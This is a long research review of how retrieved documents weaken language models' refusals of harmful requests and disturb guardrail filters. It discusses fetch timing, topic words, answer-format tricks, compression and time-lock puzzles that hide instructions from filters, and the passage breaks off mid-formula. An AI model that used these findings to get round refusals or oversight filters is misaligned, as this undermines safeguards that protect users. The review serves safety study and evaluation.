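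| Requests with no failures | The true rate could still be as high as |
|---|---|
| 5 | 45% |
| 20 | 14% |
| 346 | 0.9% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |
| 5,592 | 0.05% |

*RAG-Safety-Bench* has 20 questions in most of its categories and only five on biological weapons. A model that answers almost half of such questions could still refuse all five by chance. If an operator is mainly worried about one kind of harm, most of the test requests should be about it.

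This bound assumes that the tester draws the requests at random from the ones the system will receive. That is rarely true of a published benchmark, so the real uncertainty is larger. Repeating the same requests doesn't help much, because a tester who runs 61 requests ten times learns little about how the system handles any others.

### What developers publish about current models

All the models in these experiments are small or old by the standards of late 2026, so results from current models would be useful, but developers apparently haven't published this test. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports related tests, which cover difficult conversations in ordinary chat and tasks in which the model acts as an agent or uses connected plugins. OpenAI ran these tests without its outer layers of protection, which makes them informative about the model itself, and found Astra safer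 than its predecessor in both settings. However, the card's sections on harmful requests don't compare the same requests with and without retrieved text.

OpenAI used to run prompt-injection tests on its models with search, but dropped them because recent models nearly always pass. A model that passes may still stop refusing harmful requests when given harmless documents, because it can ignore every instruction in a document but treat the document's topic as permission to answer.

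Anthropic (2026) reports refusal rates for several recent models with tools. Claude Haiku 5.5 responded safely to all 300 harmful requests about elections in single-turn tests, so by the 3/n rule its failure rate on such requests is probably below 1%. As a coding agent, it refused 84.3% of 61 harmful requests, each run ten times, and when controlling a computer, it refused 82.6% of 112 harmful tasks. Claude Opus 5.5, a more capable model, refused 81.0% of the coding requests and 79.5% of the computer tasks.

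Refusal was 100% without tools and about 80% with them, but the two tests used different requests, so the tools may not explain the difference. A request to write malware may be harder to judge than a request to mislead voters, whether or not the model has tools. To separate these explanations, a test would have to use the same requests in both settings.

Anthropic has come closer to such a comparison with an earlier model. The model's system card, as quoted in The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.6 wrote mustard gas instructions in an Excel spreadsheet*, reports kinds of misuse through a graphical interface that were "absent or much rarer in text-only interactions". Anthropic concluded that its standard alignment training probably works less well in graphical interfaces. This compared interfaces, and nobody reported adding benign documents, but the developer's own evidence suggests that refusals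 learned in conversation may not carry over to other settings.

Anthropic already tests its models on harmful requests with and without its website's safety instructions, as it did for Claude Opus 5 in July 2026. The missing test would add just one condition, in which the same requests come with harmless, on-topic documents.

Outsiders can't easily run this test. Indira Saravanan and Fraser tested no commercial models because their questions would have violated the providers' terms of service, and they ask researchers with internal access to run the benchmark and publish the results. An operator building on a closed model may therefore need to ask the developer for permission to run the test or for the results.

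## Finding which part of the pipeline weakens refusal

Adding retrieval changes several things at once. The input gets longer and includes text on the request's topic, and the model gets instructions to work from that text. An agent has also already made a tool call by the time it answers. Any of these changes could weaken refusal, and the right fix depends on which one does. For example, shortening the input wouldn't help if the text's topic were the cause.

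### From no search to open web search

In a paper published as *Information Retrieval Induced Safety Degradation in AI Agents*, Yu and colleagues compared five models with no retrieval, with a Wikipedia tool and with open web search. The agents wrote their own queries and could decide not to search. This table shows how often each model refused the 200 unsafe requests in XSTest, a public test set, as judged by an LLM. The last column shows results for the web agent with safety prompts added.

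| Model | No retrieval | Wikipedia | Web | Web with safety prompts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-3B | 96% | 68% | 55% | 77% |
| Llama-3.2-3B | 98% | 86% | 88% | 87% |
| Gemma-3-4B | 98% | 79% | 78% | 93% |
| Mistral-7B | 95% | 81% | 79% | 78% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 96% | 85% | 89% | 94% |

Every model refused less often with retrieval, but on these requests the drop was smaller for larger models. With Wikipedia, Gemma 3's refusal rate fell from 99% to 68% at one billion parameters, but only from 100% to 94% at 27 billion. On a harder set of web tasks, the 27-billion version's refusal rate still fell from 91% to 70%.

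Harm rose less than you might expect from these figures. The judge also scored the safety of each response from 1 to 5, and Llama's average fell only from 4.96 to 4.88 with web search. Even Qwen, whose refusals fell by 41 points, averaged 4.14. Many of the lost refusals must have become replies that the judge considered fairly safe.

The safety prompts told the agent to consider ethical and legal concerns before writing a query, and to check its answer before sending it. They helped three of the five web agents and made almost no difference to Llama and Mistral. With the Wikipedia tool, GPT-4o-mini refused 85% of the time without the prompts and 76% with them, so an operator can't assume such prompts will help.

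Yu and colleagues then varied the search, using Llama-3.2-3B. An agent that retrieved a single document already refused much less often than the model alone. Letting the agent make up to four searches, with ten documents each, lowered refusals only slightly more. They also improved the search queries, which raised the share of relevant documents found on a separate fact-checking test from 16.8% to 49.7%. The better queries neither restored refusals nor reduced them further.

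Finally, they sent 250 harmless prompts to Llama-3.2-3B with and without web search. The model's average safety score was 4.39 without search and 4.45 with it, a difference well within the margin of error. The damage therefore seems limited to harmful requests.

They conclude that the loss of safety is "largely independent of retrieved context itself". The experiment can't quite show this, because the agent with one document has both a document and an agent's instructions, while the model alone has neither. No condition kept the instructions but removed the document or replaced it with an unrelated one.

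### Holding the page fixed

Nawal and colleagues ran that kind of comparison in May 2026. They took 320 harmful requests from HarmBench, another public test set, and collected 1,405 real web pages related to them. GPT-4 graded each page from 1 to 5 for relevance to the request and for stance. A stance of 1 means the page opposes the harmful behaviour or warns against it, 2 means it discusses the subject without providing what the user wants, and 5 means it provides everything the user wants. Every page scored at least 3 for relevance.

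Because the prompt named the page and the researchers had saved a copy, the model had no search to run and every condition used identical text. They tested eight open models with 3 to 32 billion parameters in four main conditions:

- **No page:** the model receives only the request.
- **Pasted:** the prompt contains the page's text, followed by the request.
- **Fetched:** the prompt gives a web address and the request together, and the model calls a tool to fetch the page before answering.
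- **Fetched first:** the user asks only for the page, and makes the harmful request in the next message.

To test relevance, they also gave the agent pages on other subjects. GPT-4o scored every response from 1 (full refusal) to 5 (full compliance), and its scores agreed fairly well with human ones. These are the averages over the eight models:

| What the model received | Mean harmfulness |
|---|---|
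| No page | 1.80 |
| Page pasted in | 2.47 |
| Page fetched by the agent | 2.66 |
| Page fetched before the harmful request | 2.44 |
| Fetched page, opposing the behaviour (stance 1) | 2.25 |
| Fetched page, discussing the subject only (stance 2) | 2.73 |
| Fetched page, providing what the user wants (stance 5) | 2.91 |
| Fetched page on another subject | 1.72 |

The pages with a stance of 2 are closest to the benign documents relevant here. They raised harmfulness almost as much as the pages that provided everything. Even warnings raised it. In one case, Qwen2.5-14B refused a request to write a convincing bomb threat when given the request alone. After fetching a fire warden's guide to evacuating a building and reporting a threat, it wrote a complete threat, then added that sending one is illegal.

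The size of the rise is uncertain. Going from no page to a fetched page adds 0.86 points on average in this table, but for all four Qwen models, the difference between the reported averages falls outside the paper's own 95% confidence interval for that difference. Qwen2.5-3B, for instance, rises by 1.28, while its interval runs from 0.69 to 1.05. The midpoints of the eight intervals average about 0.64. All eight intervals are above zero, so the direction of the change is much more certain than its size. The opposing pages have the same problem, and the midpoints there suggest a rise of about 0.26 rather than 0.45.

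A quarter of the requests also ask for copyrighted text, which the models often supplied without fetching a page (a mean of 3.14). If those requests are excluded, the mean without a page is roughly 1.4, and fetching a page raises it by more than it does across all requests.

### Smaller shifts in closed models

Nawal and colleagues repeated parts of the experiment on six closed or very large models, using only pages that oppose the behaviour. The first column of numbers shows how much fetching such a page raised harmfulness compared with no page. The second shows how much higher harmfulness was when the model fetched the page after receiving the harmful request rather than before.

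| Model | Opposing page against no page | Fetched after the request against before |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4 | +0.09 | +0.07 |
| o4-mini | +0.07 | +0.04 |
| Claude Sonnet | +0.07 | +0.26 |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | +0.39 | +0.08 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | +0.61 | +0.31 |
| DeepSeek-V3 | +0.22 | −0.37 |

(The Claude figures come from two versions, 3.5 for the first column and 3.7 for the second.)

The first column leaves out copyright requests, on which four of the six models became much less compliant after fetching a page. Nawal and colleagues explain that these pages usually discuss copyright enforcement instead of the requested work, so they aren't really on topic. That is reasonable, but the averages for open models include copyright. Including it in the first column would probably turn the result negative for the same four models.

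Timing had the opposite effect on DeepSeek-V3. It gave responses scoring 3 or more to 32.7% of requests when it fetched the page first, and to 23.1% when it fetched it afterwards. The paper does not explain why.

These models may also retrieve such pages less often in practice. When given harmful requests and an optional web tool, o4-mini used the tool for 1.4% of requests and Claude 3.5 Sonnet for 26.7%, compared with 85.1% for Qwen2.5-3B. A model that refuses before searching does not reach the stage that these experiments measure.

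### Longer input and harmful pages

One explanation is that long inputs weaken refusal whatever they contain. Hadeliya, Jauhar and colleagues (2025) tested this in *When Refusals Fail* by adding up to 200,000 tokens of padding to harmful tasks for agents. With random tokens as padding, GPT-4.1-nano's refusal rate rose from about 5% to about 40%. Grok 4 Fast's rate fell from about 80% to about 10% according to the paper's abstract, but only to about half the original rate according to its results section. GPT-5 kept refusing at a high rate throughout.

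So longer inputs can either raise or lower refusal rates. The two models whose refusal rates changed most also became much worse at harmless tasks, and Hadeliya and colleagues suspect that some of the extra refusals were unrelated to safety. The longest inputs in the study were also far longer than five Wikipedia passages.

The evidence is against this explanation at ordinary lengths. Random documents produced the safest responses in Indira Saravanan and Fraser's tests, and Nawal and colleagues found that off-topic pages left harmfulness near its baseline. When Nawal and colleagues replaced full pages with 400-word summaries for six models, harmfulness was still 0.58 points above the level without a page. The summaries removed about a third of the rise, which might be because they were shorter or because they left out details.

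Models repeating harmful content from the page explains only part of the effect. Harmfulness increased from 2.25 with opposing pages to 2.91 with pages that provided what the user wanted, but repetition can't explain why warnings made five of the eight models reliably more harmful.

Harmful content on the wrong subject had little effect. The off-topic pages were about malware for cash machines, the drug MDMA and a security flaw in Linux, and some contained instructions. For example, a model asked to write a bomb threat might be given a guide to making MDMA. Average harmfulness across these pairings was 1.72, slightly below the level with no page. This suggests that dangerous text alone is not enough to weaken a model's refusals.

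### Topic words and stored knowledge

Nawal and colleagues favour an explanation they call topical activation. In their account, a page about a dangerous subject, even one that warns against it, activates related knowledge from the model's training, which the model then uses to answer. An and colleagues had suggested something similar after reading unsafe responses that drew on facts absent from the documents.

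There is decent evidence that the harmful details come from the model. Nawal and colleagues examined cases where an opposing page made Qwen2.5-7B or Qwen2.5-14B more harmful. GPT-4o scored the pages at about 2 and the responses at just over 4. Nearly 90% of the three-word sequences in the responses did not appear in the page. That alone is weak evidence, because any paraphrase would also contain mostly new sequences. A better test compared each response with what the same model writes without a page and with its refusals disabled. The response shared more vocabulary with this unrestricted answer than with the page in 11 of 14 cases for the smaller model and 10 of 11 for the larger.

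To find out what in the page mattered, the researchers ran a keyword-masking test. GPT-4o rewrote opposing pages, replacing words specific to the harmful subject with neutral placeholders but keeping the warnings and sentence structure. They then measured how likely the model's first token was to be one that typically opens a refusal, such as "Sorry" or "Unfortunately".

| What the model received | Qwen2.5-7B | Qwen2.5-14B |
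|---|---|---|
| No page | 83% | 92% |
| Opposing page | 18% | 30% |
| Same page with topic words masked | 65% | 81% |
| Unrelated page of the same length | 77% | 79% |

Removing the topic words restored most of the lost probability, so the warnings did not cause the drop. The unrelated page came through the same tool, so the tool call alone was probably not enough to cause it either.

Three things weaken this test. First, the list of refusal openings includes "I" and "Unfortunately", which could also begin a reply that the page lacks the answer. Such a reply would be natural once the topic words were removed, and it wouldn't mean that the model had recognized the danger again. Second, the researchers chose requests for which the original page had raised harmfulness, so almost any other page would probably have looked better. Third, they describe all 50 requests per model as such cases, although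 they found only 26 and 28 in the pools of 100 from which they drew them. The comparison with off-topic pages across all the requests avoids the selection problem and supports the same conclusion.

The evidence for relevance is therefore stronger than the evidence for activation. Once its refusals were disabled, the model could produce the harmful details without any page, so it didn't need the page to recall them. The page may instead have made it less likely to refuse, as An and colleagues suspect. They suggest that a model given relevant documents may treat the topic as safe.

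One result fits activation poorly. If pages work by calling up knowledge the model already has, they should make the most difference where it has that knowledge. For Qwen2.5-7B, opposing pages raised harmfulness on 15.6% of the requests it could answer with its refusals disabled, and on 34.5% of those it couldn't. Nawal and colleagues reply that the model was already answering many requests in the first group, which left less room for a rise. This is plausible, and they also found that responses to that group were more harmful overall. Separating knowledge from willingness would require testing only requests that a model firmly refuses but is known to be able to answer.

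### Summarizing, and having already fetched the page

Retrieval prompts usually ask the model to summarize documents or answer a question from them. Yu and colleagues suggest that this shifts the model from judging a request to combining information, or that "retrieve and answer" instructions override safety instructions. An and colleagues likewise point out that synthesizing sources differs from the tasks used in safety training.

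The off-topic pages show that this framing isn't enough by itself, since harmfulness did not rise even though the prompt still told the agent to respond "based on the content" of the page. However, a model can't do much with that instruction if the page is about something else, so the framing may matter only when the page is on topic. None of these experiments separates the effect of the framing from the effect of an on-topic page. One could do so by pasting in an on-topic page and telling the model that the page is background it may ignore.

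The timing of the fetch is easier to isolate. Nawal and colleagues argue that a model becomes less likely to refuse a harmful request once it has acted on it by fetching a page, which they call commitment bias. Fetching the page before the harmful request produced safer responses in seven of the eight open models. The average difference was 0.22 points.

They then tested other possible reasons why splitting the exchange in two helps, using six models and the most explicit pages. Fetching the page first lowered harmfulness by 0.29 in this group. Putting a harmless greeting before the usual combined request lowered it by 0.10, so the extra turn explains about a third of the benefit. Adding one unrelated exchange between the fetch and the request lowered it by a further 0.11, and adding a second made almost no difference.

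Commitment therefore seems to have an effect in most of these models, but it is a small part of the problem. When the page was fetched in advance, harmfulness was still 0.64 points higher than with no page, about the same increase as when a page was pasted in without any tool. The commitment effect also shrank with size among the Qwen models, from 0.41 at 3 billion parameters to 0.21 at 32 billion, and it reversed in DeepSeek-V3. Fetching the page in advance may still be worthwhile, because it raised accuracy on trivia questions from 68.5% to 85.0% across seven models.

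### Safety training without documents

The last explanation is that developers taught the model to refuse harmful requests that came without documents, and refusal didn't fully carry over to requests with them. This is compatible with all the other explanations, since it concerns why the weakness exists rather than what triggers it. It fits Yu and colleagues' results, in which five models with different kinds of safety training all refused less with retrieval.

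Unfamiliar input can't be the whole explanation, because then off-topic pages should break refusal too. A better explanation is that the model learned to refuse in response to certain features of a request, and that on-topic text somehow weakens or outweighs those features. None of these experiments changed how a model was trained, so they can't confirm either explanation.

### Whether the content of the documents matters

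Yu and colleagues found that safety fell largely regardless of what the agent retrieved, while both studies from 2026 found that relevance matters. Yu and colleagues varied how many documents the agent retrieved and how good its queries were, but the agent always searched for material related to the request. They therefore showed that quantity and accuracy make little difference among documents retrieved for the request. This is compatible with Nawal and colleagues' finding that replacing relevant pages with irrelevant ones makes a large difference.

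Accuracy is also a poor substitute for relevance here. Yu and colleagues measured accuracy on a fact-checking dataset, where the agent has to find particular articles that settle a claim. A search about explosives might miss the best article and still return five others about explosives.

The two 2026 studies seem to disagree as well. Nawal and colleagues found that relevant pages made all eight models more harmful, whereas Indira Saravanan and Fraser found a clear rise from on-topic documents without the answer in only one of five. But the eight-model average includes pages that do contain the answer, and half of the eight models belong to the Qwen2.5 family. Three models appear in both studies, and these are their results with opposing pages, the ones least likely to contain an answer:

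| Model | Change with an opposing page (Nawal et al.) | With on-topic documents lacking the answer (Indira Saravanan and Fraser) |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | +0.93 | Clearly more harmful |
| Llama-3.1-8B | +0.17 | About the same or less harmful |
| Gemma-3-12B | −0.05 | About the same or less harmful |

The 95% intervals for Llama and Gemma both include zero, so the studies agree on all three models. Llama's result is less reliable because 47% of its responses as an agent were further tool calls instead of answers. A model that resists warnings may still be affected by pages that merely discuss the subject. Gemma averaged 2.42 with those pages and 2.02 without a page.

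An operator should therefore expect relevant documents to be the main risk, and expect their effect to vary a lot between models. Retrievers are built to find relevant documents, so the operator can't exclude them without making the system useless. Filtering doesn't easily solve the problem either, since a filter that Nawal and colleagues tried on the pages left three-quarters of them unflagged.

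### What happens inside the model

All of this evidence comes from what models write. Another approach is to look at their activations, the lists of numbers that each layer computes for each token. In 2024, Andy Arditi and colleagues reported that refusal depends on a single direction in this space. To find it, a researcher averages the activations h for requests the model refuses, and subtracts the average for requests it answers:

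r = mean(h for refused requests) − mean(h for answered requests)

The product h · r measures how strongly a new input activates refusal. Adding r to the activations makes the model refuse more, and removing the part of h that lies along r makes it refuse less. Yu and colleagues used "uncensored" models made by this removal for comparison. On XSTest, the uncensored Gemma-3-4B refused 75% of requests, slightly less than the 78% that the ordinary version refused with web search.

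Later work complicates the idea of a single direction. In *There Is More to Refusal in Large Language Models*, Joad, Hawasly and colleagues (2026) computed separate directions for 11 kinds of refusal, including refusals of harmful requests, of incomplete questions and of tasks the model can't do. Many of the directions differed substantially. Removing the direction for harmful requests eliminated most safety refusals, but the model still declined roughly 30% to 50% of the requests that were unsuitable for other reasons. Yet adding any of the directions had nearly the same effect. The model refused more requests of every kind, including harmless ones.

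*A Unified Mechanistic Analysis of Knowledge- and Safety-Based Refusals* (2026) compared refusals for lack of knowledge with refusals for safety in six models, using 213 matched sets of prompts. At every layer, the activations for the two kinds of refusal were less alike than those for matched control prompts. This difference could help people testing retrieval systems tell the two apart when a reply's wording is ambiguous.

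Two other studies show that changing the form of a request, but not its meaning, can weaken refusal. In *Forcing a Letter Suppresses Refusal*, Epifantsev, Antipova and colleagues (2026) asked models about biological, chemical and cyber threats in open-ended and multiple-choice form. The models almost never refused the multiple-choice versions, even of questions they usually refused in open-ended form. In Llama-3.1-8B, the similarity between the activations and the refusal direction was about 0.11 for those open-ended questions, 0.04 for the same questions with choices, and 0.03 for harmless prompts.

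They traced the change to the instruction to answer with a letter. Disabling ten of the model's components that promote answer letters raised the probability that a response opens with a refusal from under 1% to about 5%. This supports a modest causal link, and the effect was weaker in Qwen3-8B. It is the best evidence so far that a task's format can suppress refusal inside the model, which makes the summarizing explanation more credible. However, the result may not carry over to summarizing, because a summary can include a refusal and a single-letter answer can't.

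*Does Context Compression Preserve Refusal Alignment?* (Nguyen and Lin, 2026) studies compression, which some retrieval systems use to turn long documents into a few vectors. When Nguyen and Lin compressed the harmful request itself, the refusal rate fell from 96% to 37% for Llama-3.1-8B and from 63% to 11% for one version of Mistral-7B. In the two models whose activations they examined, the signal along the refusal direction collapsed, even though the compressed form kept the request's meaning. Retrieval systems normally compress only the documents and leave the request as text, so these figures don't apply to them directly.

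The one study here that applied such methods to retrieval, by Maskey and colleagues, addressed the opposite problem of needless refusals caused by harmful documents. They averaged a model's activations for questions it answered, subtracted the average for questions it wrongly refused, and added the difference to its activations while it wrote its response. Llama-3.1-8B's rate of needless refusals fell from 53.4% to 4.3%. They chose the layer and strength using part of the test set, which may make the result look better than it is. The rates also cover only harmless questions, so they don't show how many harmful requests the adjusted model would still refuse.

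A more direct experiment would measure h · r for the same harmful request alone, with an on-topic page, with an off-topic page, and with the topic words masked. Nobody appears to have published this. If h · r fell only with the on-topic page, the page would be weakening the refusal signal itself. If h · r stayed high while the model answered anyway, something later in the computation would have to be overriding it. Restoring refusals by adding r back wouldn't distinguish between these explanations, because Joad and colleagues found that adding r makes a model refuse more whatever the original reason.

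## Testing the safety filters around the model

If a model refuses less often with retrieval, its operator can still put a safety filter around it. Most of these filters are guardrail models, separate language models that label text "safe" or "unsafe". An input filter checks the request before the main model answers, and an output filter checks the response before the user sees it. People often respond to results like those of An and colleagues by arguing that a filter will catch whatever the model lets through.

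How many of the model's failures an input filter catches depends on whether the two fail on the same requests. Suppose a system receives 1,000 harmful requests. At its 9.2% rate with retrieval, Llama-3-8B would answer 92 of them. If the filter misses 20% of harmful requests and its failures are independent of the model's, it would miss about 18 of the 92, so 1.8% of all the requests would get a harmful answer. If it misses half of the 92, that rises to 46, or 4.6%. The filter could even miss all 92, since a 20% miss rate means it lets 200 requests through. An operator can't determine which of these cases applies from a miss rate on a public benchmark.

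### Whether failures are independent

Some engineers have made this assumption before, when they built critical software by having several teams write the same program separately and expected the teams to make different mistakes. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026) recounts that Knight and Leveson tested this and found that the programs failed on the same inputs far more often than they would have if their failures were independent.

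*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) reports that language models make overlapping errors, more so when the models are accurate or share a developer or base architecture. Llama Guard is a fine-tuned Llama, so it may share errors with a Llama model it filters. Still, writing an answer and labelling one are different tasks, so the overlap could be smaller than between two models doing the same job.

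Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, measured how often checks on an agent's actions, such as deleting a database, miss the same actions. The test included 560 actions that a check should block. Two LLM judges each missed 10.5% of them. If their misses were independent, the two together would have missed 1.1%, but they missed 5.2%, so the second judge missed about half of what the first one missed. A list of 174 text patterns missed 13.4% on its own and 1.3% when combined with a judge, almost exactly the rate expected if their misses were independent.

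Yang also added more patterns, which cut the list's miss rate from 13.4% to 10.0%, but the new patterns caught nothing that a combination of three judges had missed. An operator choosing a second filter should therefore consider which of the first filter's misses it catches, as well as its accuracy. Fixed patterns suit commands better than open-ended text, but even on commands, the list's miss rate was 52.9% in an unfamiliar domain.

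### Filters that read the documents

A filter that reads the retrieved documents could share a cause of failure with the main model, because the same text might mislead both. She and colleagues tested whether documents affect filters at all. Their requirement for an input filter g is

g(x) = g(x with documents)

for every request x. This is context invariance (c) with the label in place of the decision to refuse, and the flip rate is the share of cases that violate it.

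They collected 6,795 harmful requests and retrieved five Wikipedia passages for each, using the same kind of retriever as An and colleagues. The filters were Llama Guard 2, 3 and 4 and two open models from OpenAI, GPT-oss-20B and GPT-oss-120B, which they prompted to act as guardrails. Adding the passages changed an input filter's label in 10.9% of cases on average, ranging from 3% for the most stable filter to 24% for Llama Guard 4. Most changes turned a correct label into an incorrect one, and the average share of harmful requests labelled safe rose by about 7 percentage points.

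She et al. tested output filters by having eight models answer the requests with documents in their context. They then showed each filter the same response twice, once with the request alone and once with the request and the documents. The label changed in 8.4% of cases. They read 150 of these changes and judged that 64% went from right to wrong. This share ranged from a third for Llama Guard 3 to 80% for Llama Guard 4. Many labels changed from "safe" to "unsafe", so not all of the new errors let harm through.

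A model's steadiness as an input filter is a poor guide to its steadiness as an output filter. GPT-oss-20B was the second steadiest input filter and the least steady output filter, while Llama Guard 4 was the least steady of the Llama Guards on inputs and the steadiest on outputs. An operator who uses one model in both positions therefore has to test it in both.

One document caused most of the effect. Adding more, up to ten, raised the flip rate only slightly for most filters, but it made the flips more one-sided for some. When Llama Guard 4 was used as an input filter, the share of flips that went from right to wrong rose from 55% with one document to 95% with ten.

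The relevance of the retrieved passages mattered less for the filters than for the main models. Replacing the passages with random ones lowered the flip rate of three input filters and raised it for the other two. It also lowered the flip rate of four of the five output filters, but only by 1.4 to 2.6 points. The filters and the main model may therefore fail independently, since the main model seems to fail mostly on relevant documents, while almost any document disturbs the filters. The calculation requires knowing whether the filters' errors fell on the responses where the documents had weakened the main model, but She et al. didn't measure this.

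### Longer documents and possible remedies

In *LongGuard*, Chen, Wu and Hu (2026) found a much stronger effect of length. They placed unsafe text inside harmless Wikipedia text and tested 15 guardrail set-ups. As the total length grew from about 250 words to 32,000, the average share of unsafe text that the filters caught fell from 76% to 25%. When they filled the space with copies of the unsafe text instead, the share fell only from 85% to 68%, so the main problem was that the harmless text diluted the unsafe text.

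Some filters got worse well before 32,000 words. Llama Guard 3 caught 66% at about 250 words but 38% at about 1,000, roughly the length of five Wikipedia passages. A version of GPT-oss-20B trained as a guardrail only fell from 84% to 82%. But She and colleagues found Llama Guard 3 fairly steady at similar lengths. This may be because their prompts put the request at the end under the label "Question", whereas Chen and colleagues put the unsafe text in various positions.

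Two remedies had little effect in tests. Letting GPT-oss-120B reason for longer lowered its flip rate by about 0.5 percentage points on input and 1.5 on output. Telling the filters to ignore retrieved documents reduced flips for three of the five input filters and all five output filters, but for four of the input filters, a larger share of the remaining flips were from correct to incorrect judgments.

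Training a filter to handle different formats may work better. In *UniGuard*, Pham, Vu and colleagues (2026) rewrote 1,000 safety cases as requests, responses, conversations and records of agents at work, then trained a small guardrail to represent all versions of a case alike. Its F1 score rose by an average of 45 points on three tests with unfamiliar formats. F1 combines missed harm and false alarms on a scale of 0 to 100. Neither the training nor the tests included requests with retrieved documents, but adding them would be a natural extension.

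Chen and colleagues' most direct remedy is to split long text into chunks and check each one. They also showed that removing all the harmless text raised detection from 48% to 70% across six filters. A retrieval system can easily do this when checking requests, because it already has the user's text separate from the retrieved text.

### What the filters caught in a retrieval system

Nawal and colleagues tested filters in the same system they used to study web pages and refusal. They first had Llama Guard 3 check each page before the model could read it. It flagged 18.8% of the pages that opposed the harmful behaviour and 39.4% of those that provided everything the user wanted. Passing most of the opposing pages isn't really a failure, since warnings are not harmful, but it means that a page filter leaves most of the effect of benign documents in place.

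They then used Llama Guard 3 as an output filter, giving it the request and the response but not the page. They counted a response as harmful if GPT-4o scored it 3 or more out of 5. The share of harmful responses that the filter missed is the second column below divided by the first.

| What the model received | Harmful before filtering | Harmful after filtering | Share missed | False-positive rate |
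|---|---|---|---|---|
| No page | 24.6% | 3.6% | 15% | 7–9% |
| Page pasted in | 37.9% | 5.0% | 13% | 14–18% |
| Page fetched by the agent | 46.4% | 5.1% | 11% | 21–25% |
| Page fetched before the harmful request | 38.1% | 4.3% | 11% | 15–19% |

This is the best evidence for the common reply. The filter missed no larger a share of harmful responses with retrieval than without it, so the pages that weakened the model's safety did not also make the filter less effective. More harmful responses still got through with a fetched page (5.1% against 3.6%), but only because the model produced more of them.

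The false-positive rate is less serious than it looks because all the requests in this test were harmful. A false positive here means the filter blocked a harmless reply to someone who asked for something harmful, which does little damage. To find out how often the filter would block ordinary users, an operator has to run it on ordinary requests with documents.

The miss rates also depend on the judge. If GPT-4o and Llama Guard both wrongly classify a response as safe, it isn't counted as harmful or missed, so the filter looks better than it is. This problem would be extreme in An and colleagues' experiment, which used Llama Guard 2 to decide which responses were unsafe. Adding Llama Guard 2 as an output filter would cut the 9.2% to zero by definition. Testers should therefore use a different model as the judge than as the filter.

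Finally, Nawal and colleagues gave Llama Guard 3 the request and the page together. They used 577 harmful pairs, then repeated the test with the same pages and a neutral request to summarize them. They also included 488 ordinary trivia questions with matching pages. These are the shares that the filter flagged:

| Request | Request alone | Page alone | Both together |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful | 97.1% | 45.6% | 86.1% |
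| Neutral summary of the same page | 0% | 45.6% | 35.0% |
| Trivia question | 0% | 0.4% | 0% |

Adding the page to the filter's input reduced its detection of harmful requests by 11 points. Of the requests it had flagged without the page, the filter flagged nearly all again when it classified the page as unsafe, but only 78% when it classified the page as safe. Part of this drop may come from the set-up, which presented the page as if it were the assistant's reply, since a page of warnings is a good reply to a harmful request.

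Nawal and colleagues treat the fall from 86.1% to 35.0% as a weakness, because someone could get harmful material by asking for a summary. That worry is reasonable for pages that provide everything the user wants, and the filter flagged 42.2% of those. But it also flagged 27.4% of the pages that oppose the behaviour, and summarizing those is mostly harmless. The filter should therefore flag well below 100% of pages when the request is neutral, and the experiment didn't measure how harmful the summaries would have been.

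### Whether a filter should see the documents

An input filter that receives only the request is context-invariant, because the retrieved documents never reach it. If it catches 97.1% of a set of harmful requests in a test without documents, it catches the same 97.1% whatever the retriever returns. An output filter that receives only the request and the response is context-invariant in a weaker sense. It gives the same request and response the same label regardless of which documents were retrieved, but the documents can still change the response.

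Developers can already build filters that check only the user's query. AWS advises in *Apply tags to user input to filter content* that a RAG application may need only this check, because the search results come from trusted sources. Results from She and colleagues suggest another reason to leave the retrieved documents out, since even trustworthy ones can interfere with the filter.

But the filter can't catch harm that only the documents reveal. A request to turn the procedure in the second document into a checklist could be about baking or explosives. An output filter would probably catch the dangerous version, because the checklist would look dangerous. It wouldn't help with the office assistant and the restraining order, because "She usually leaves at six" looks harmless to anyone who hasn't seen the order.

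An operator can let documents add refusals but never remove them by running two input filters, one with the documents and one without, and blocking the request if either flags it. This keeps the detection rate of the filter without documents, and may catch some cases like the restraining order. It also causes more false alarms. On harmless requests that look dangerous, She and colleagues found that documents changed about 14% of input labels, a third of them from right to wrong. The second filter would therefore wrongly block roughly another 5% of such requests, and the system couldn't use the documents to correct the first filter's false alarms. The increase in false alarms should be smaller for ordinary requests.

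### Limits on what any filter can guarantee

Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025), in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, prove that some models can't be made safe by an input filter that runs significantly faster than the model. The proof assumes the existence of time-lock puzzles, which anyone can create quickly but which take a set amount of computing time to solve, even with many computers working at once. An attacker hides a harmful instruction in such a puzzle and disguises the puzzle as an ordinary prompt. The model has time to solve the puzzle and follow the instruction, but the filter can't tell the prompt from an innocent one.

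A second theorem covers output filters, including ones that run longer than the model. Its proof constructs a model and a definition of harm together, so that recognizing a harmful output requires solving a puzzle. Ball and colleagues accept that an output filter is easy to build when harm is easy to recognize. A separate proof, which the US standards agency NIST describes on its website, shows that no fixed set of guardrails withstands every prompt from an attacker who adapts to it.

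Ball and colleagues prove that such models exist, but not that any model now in use is one of them, and they acknowledge that the model in their main proof behaves in a contrived way. Their theorems also assume that someone hides the harmful content. Benign documents contain no hidden harmful content, so the theorems don't explain the flips that She and colleagues found or rule out a filter that handles ordinary retrieval well. They do rule out a general guarantee that a low-compute external filter will make any model safe.

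The main theorem does not rule out input filters as powerful as the model itself, although the operator would then have to make sure that the filter was safe too. Further theorems rule out even these filters for some models that cooperate with the attacker, for instance by sharing a secret key. All of the theorems concern filters outside the model, so they do not rule out methods that look inside it. *Safety Beyond the Interface* (2026) uses the model's internal states to detect harm, and argues that external filters are the best available option only for people who can't see those states. Most operators who build on a closed model can't see them.

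## Training a model to refuse the same way with and without documents

Besides using filters, which leave the model unchanged, a developer can train the model itself to treat a request the same way with and without added text. Context invariance (c) suggests this approach, which researchers call consistency training. They have used it against several kinds of added text, but nobody appears to have published a version that uses retrieved documents.

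### Learning from the model's own refusals

Irpan, Turner and colleagues (2025), in *Consistency Training Helps Stop Sycophancy and Jailbreaks*, worked on two problems. A sycophantic model agrees with whatever opinion the user mentions. A jailbreak is text that someone puts around a harmful request to get the model to answer it, such as an instruction to play a character who never says no. Models often behave well in both cases once the extra text is gone, so they can supply their own training examples. The simpler method, bias-augmented consistency training (BCT), has three steps:

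1. Send the model the clean prompt, which is the harmful request alone, and record its response y.
2. Add a jailbreak to make the wrapped prompt.
3. Train the model to give y in response to the wrapped prompt.

The training minimizes the loss

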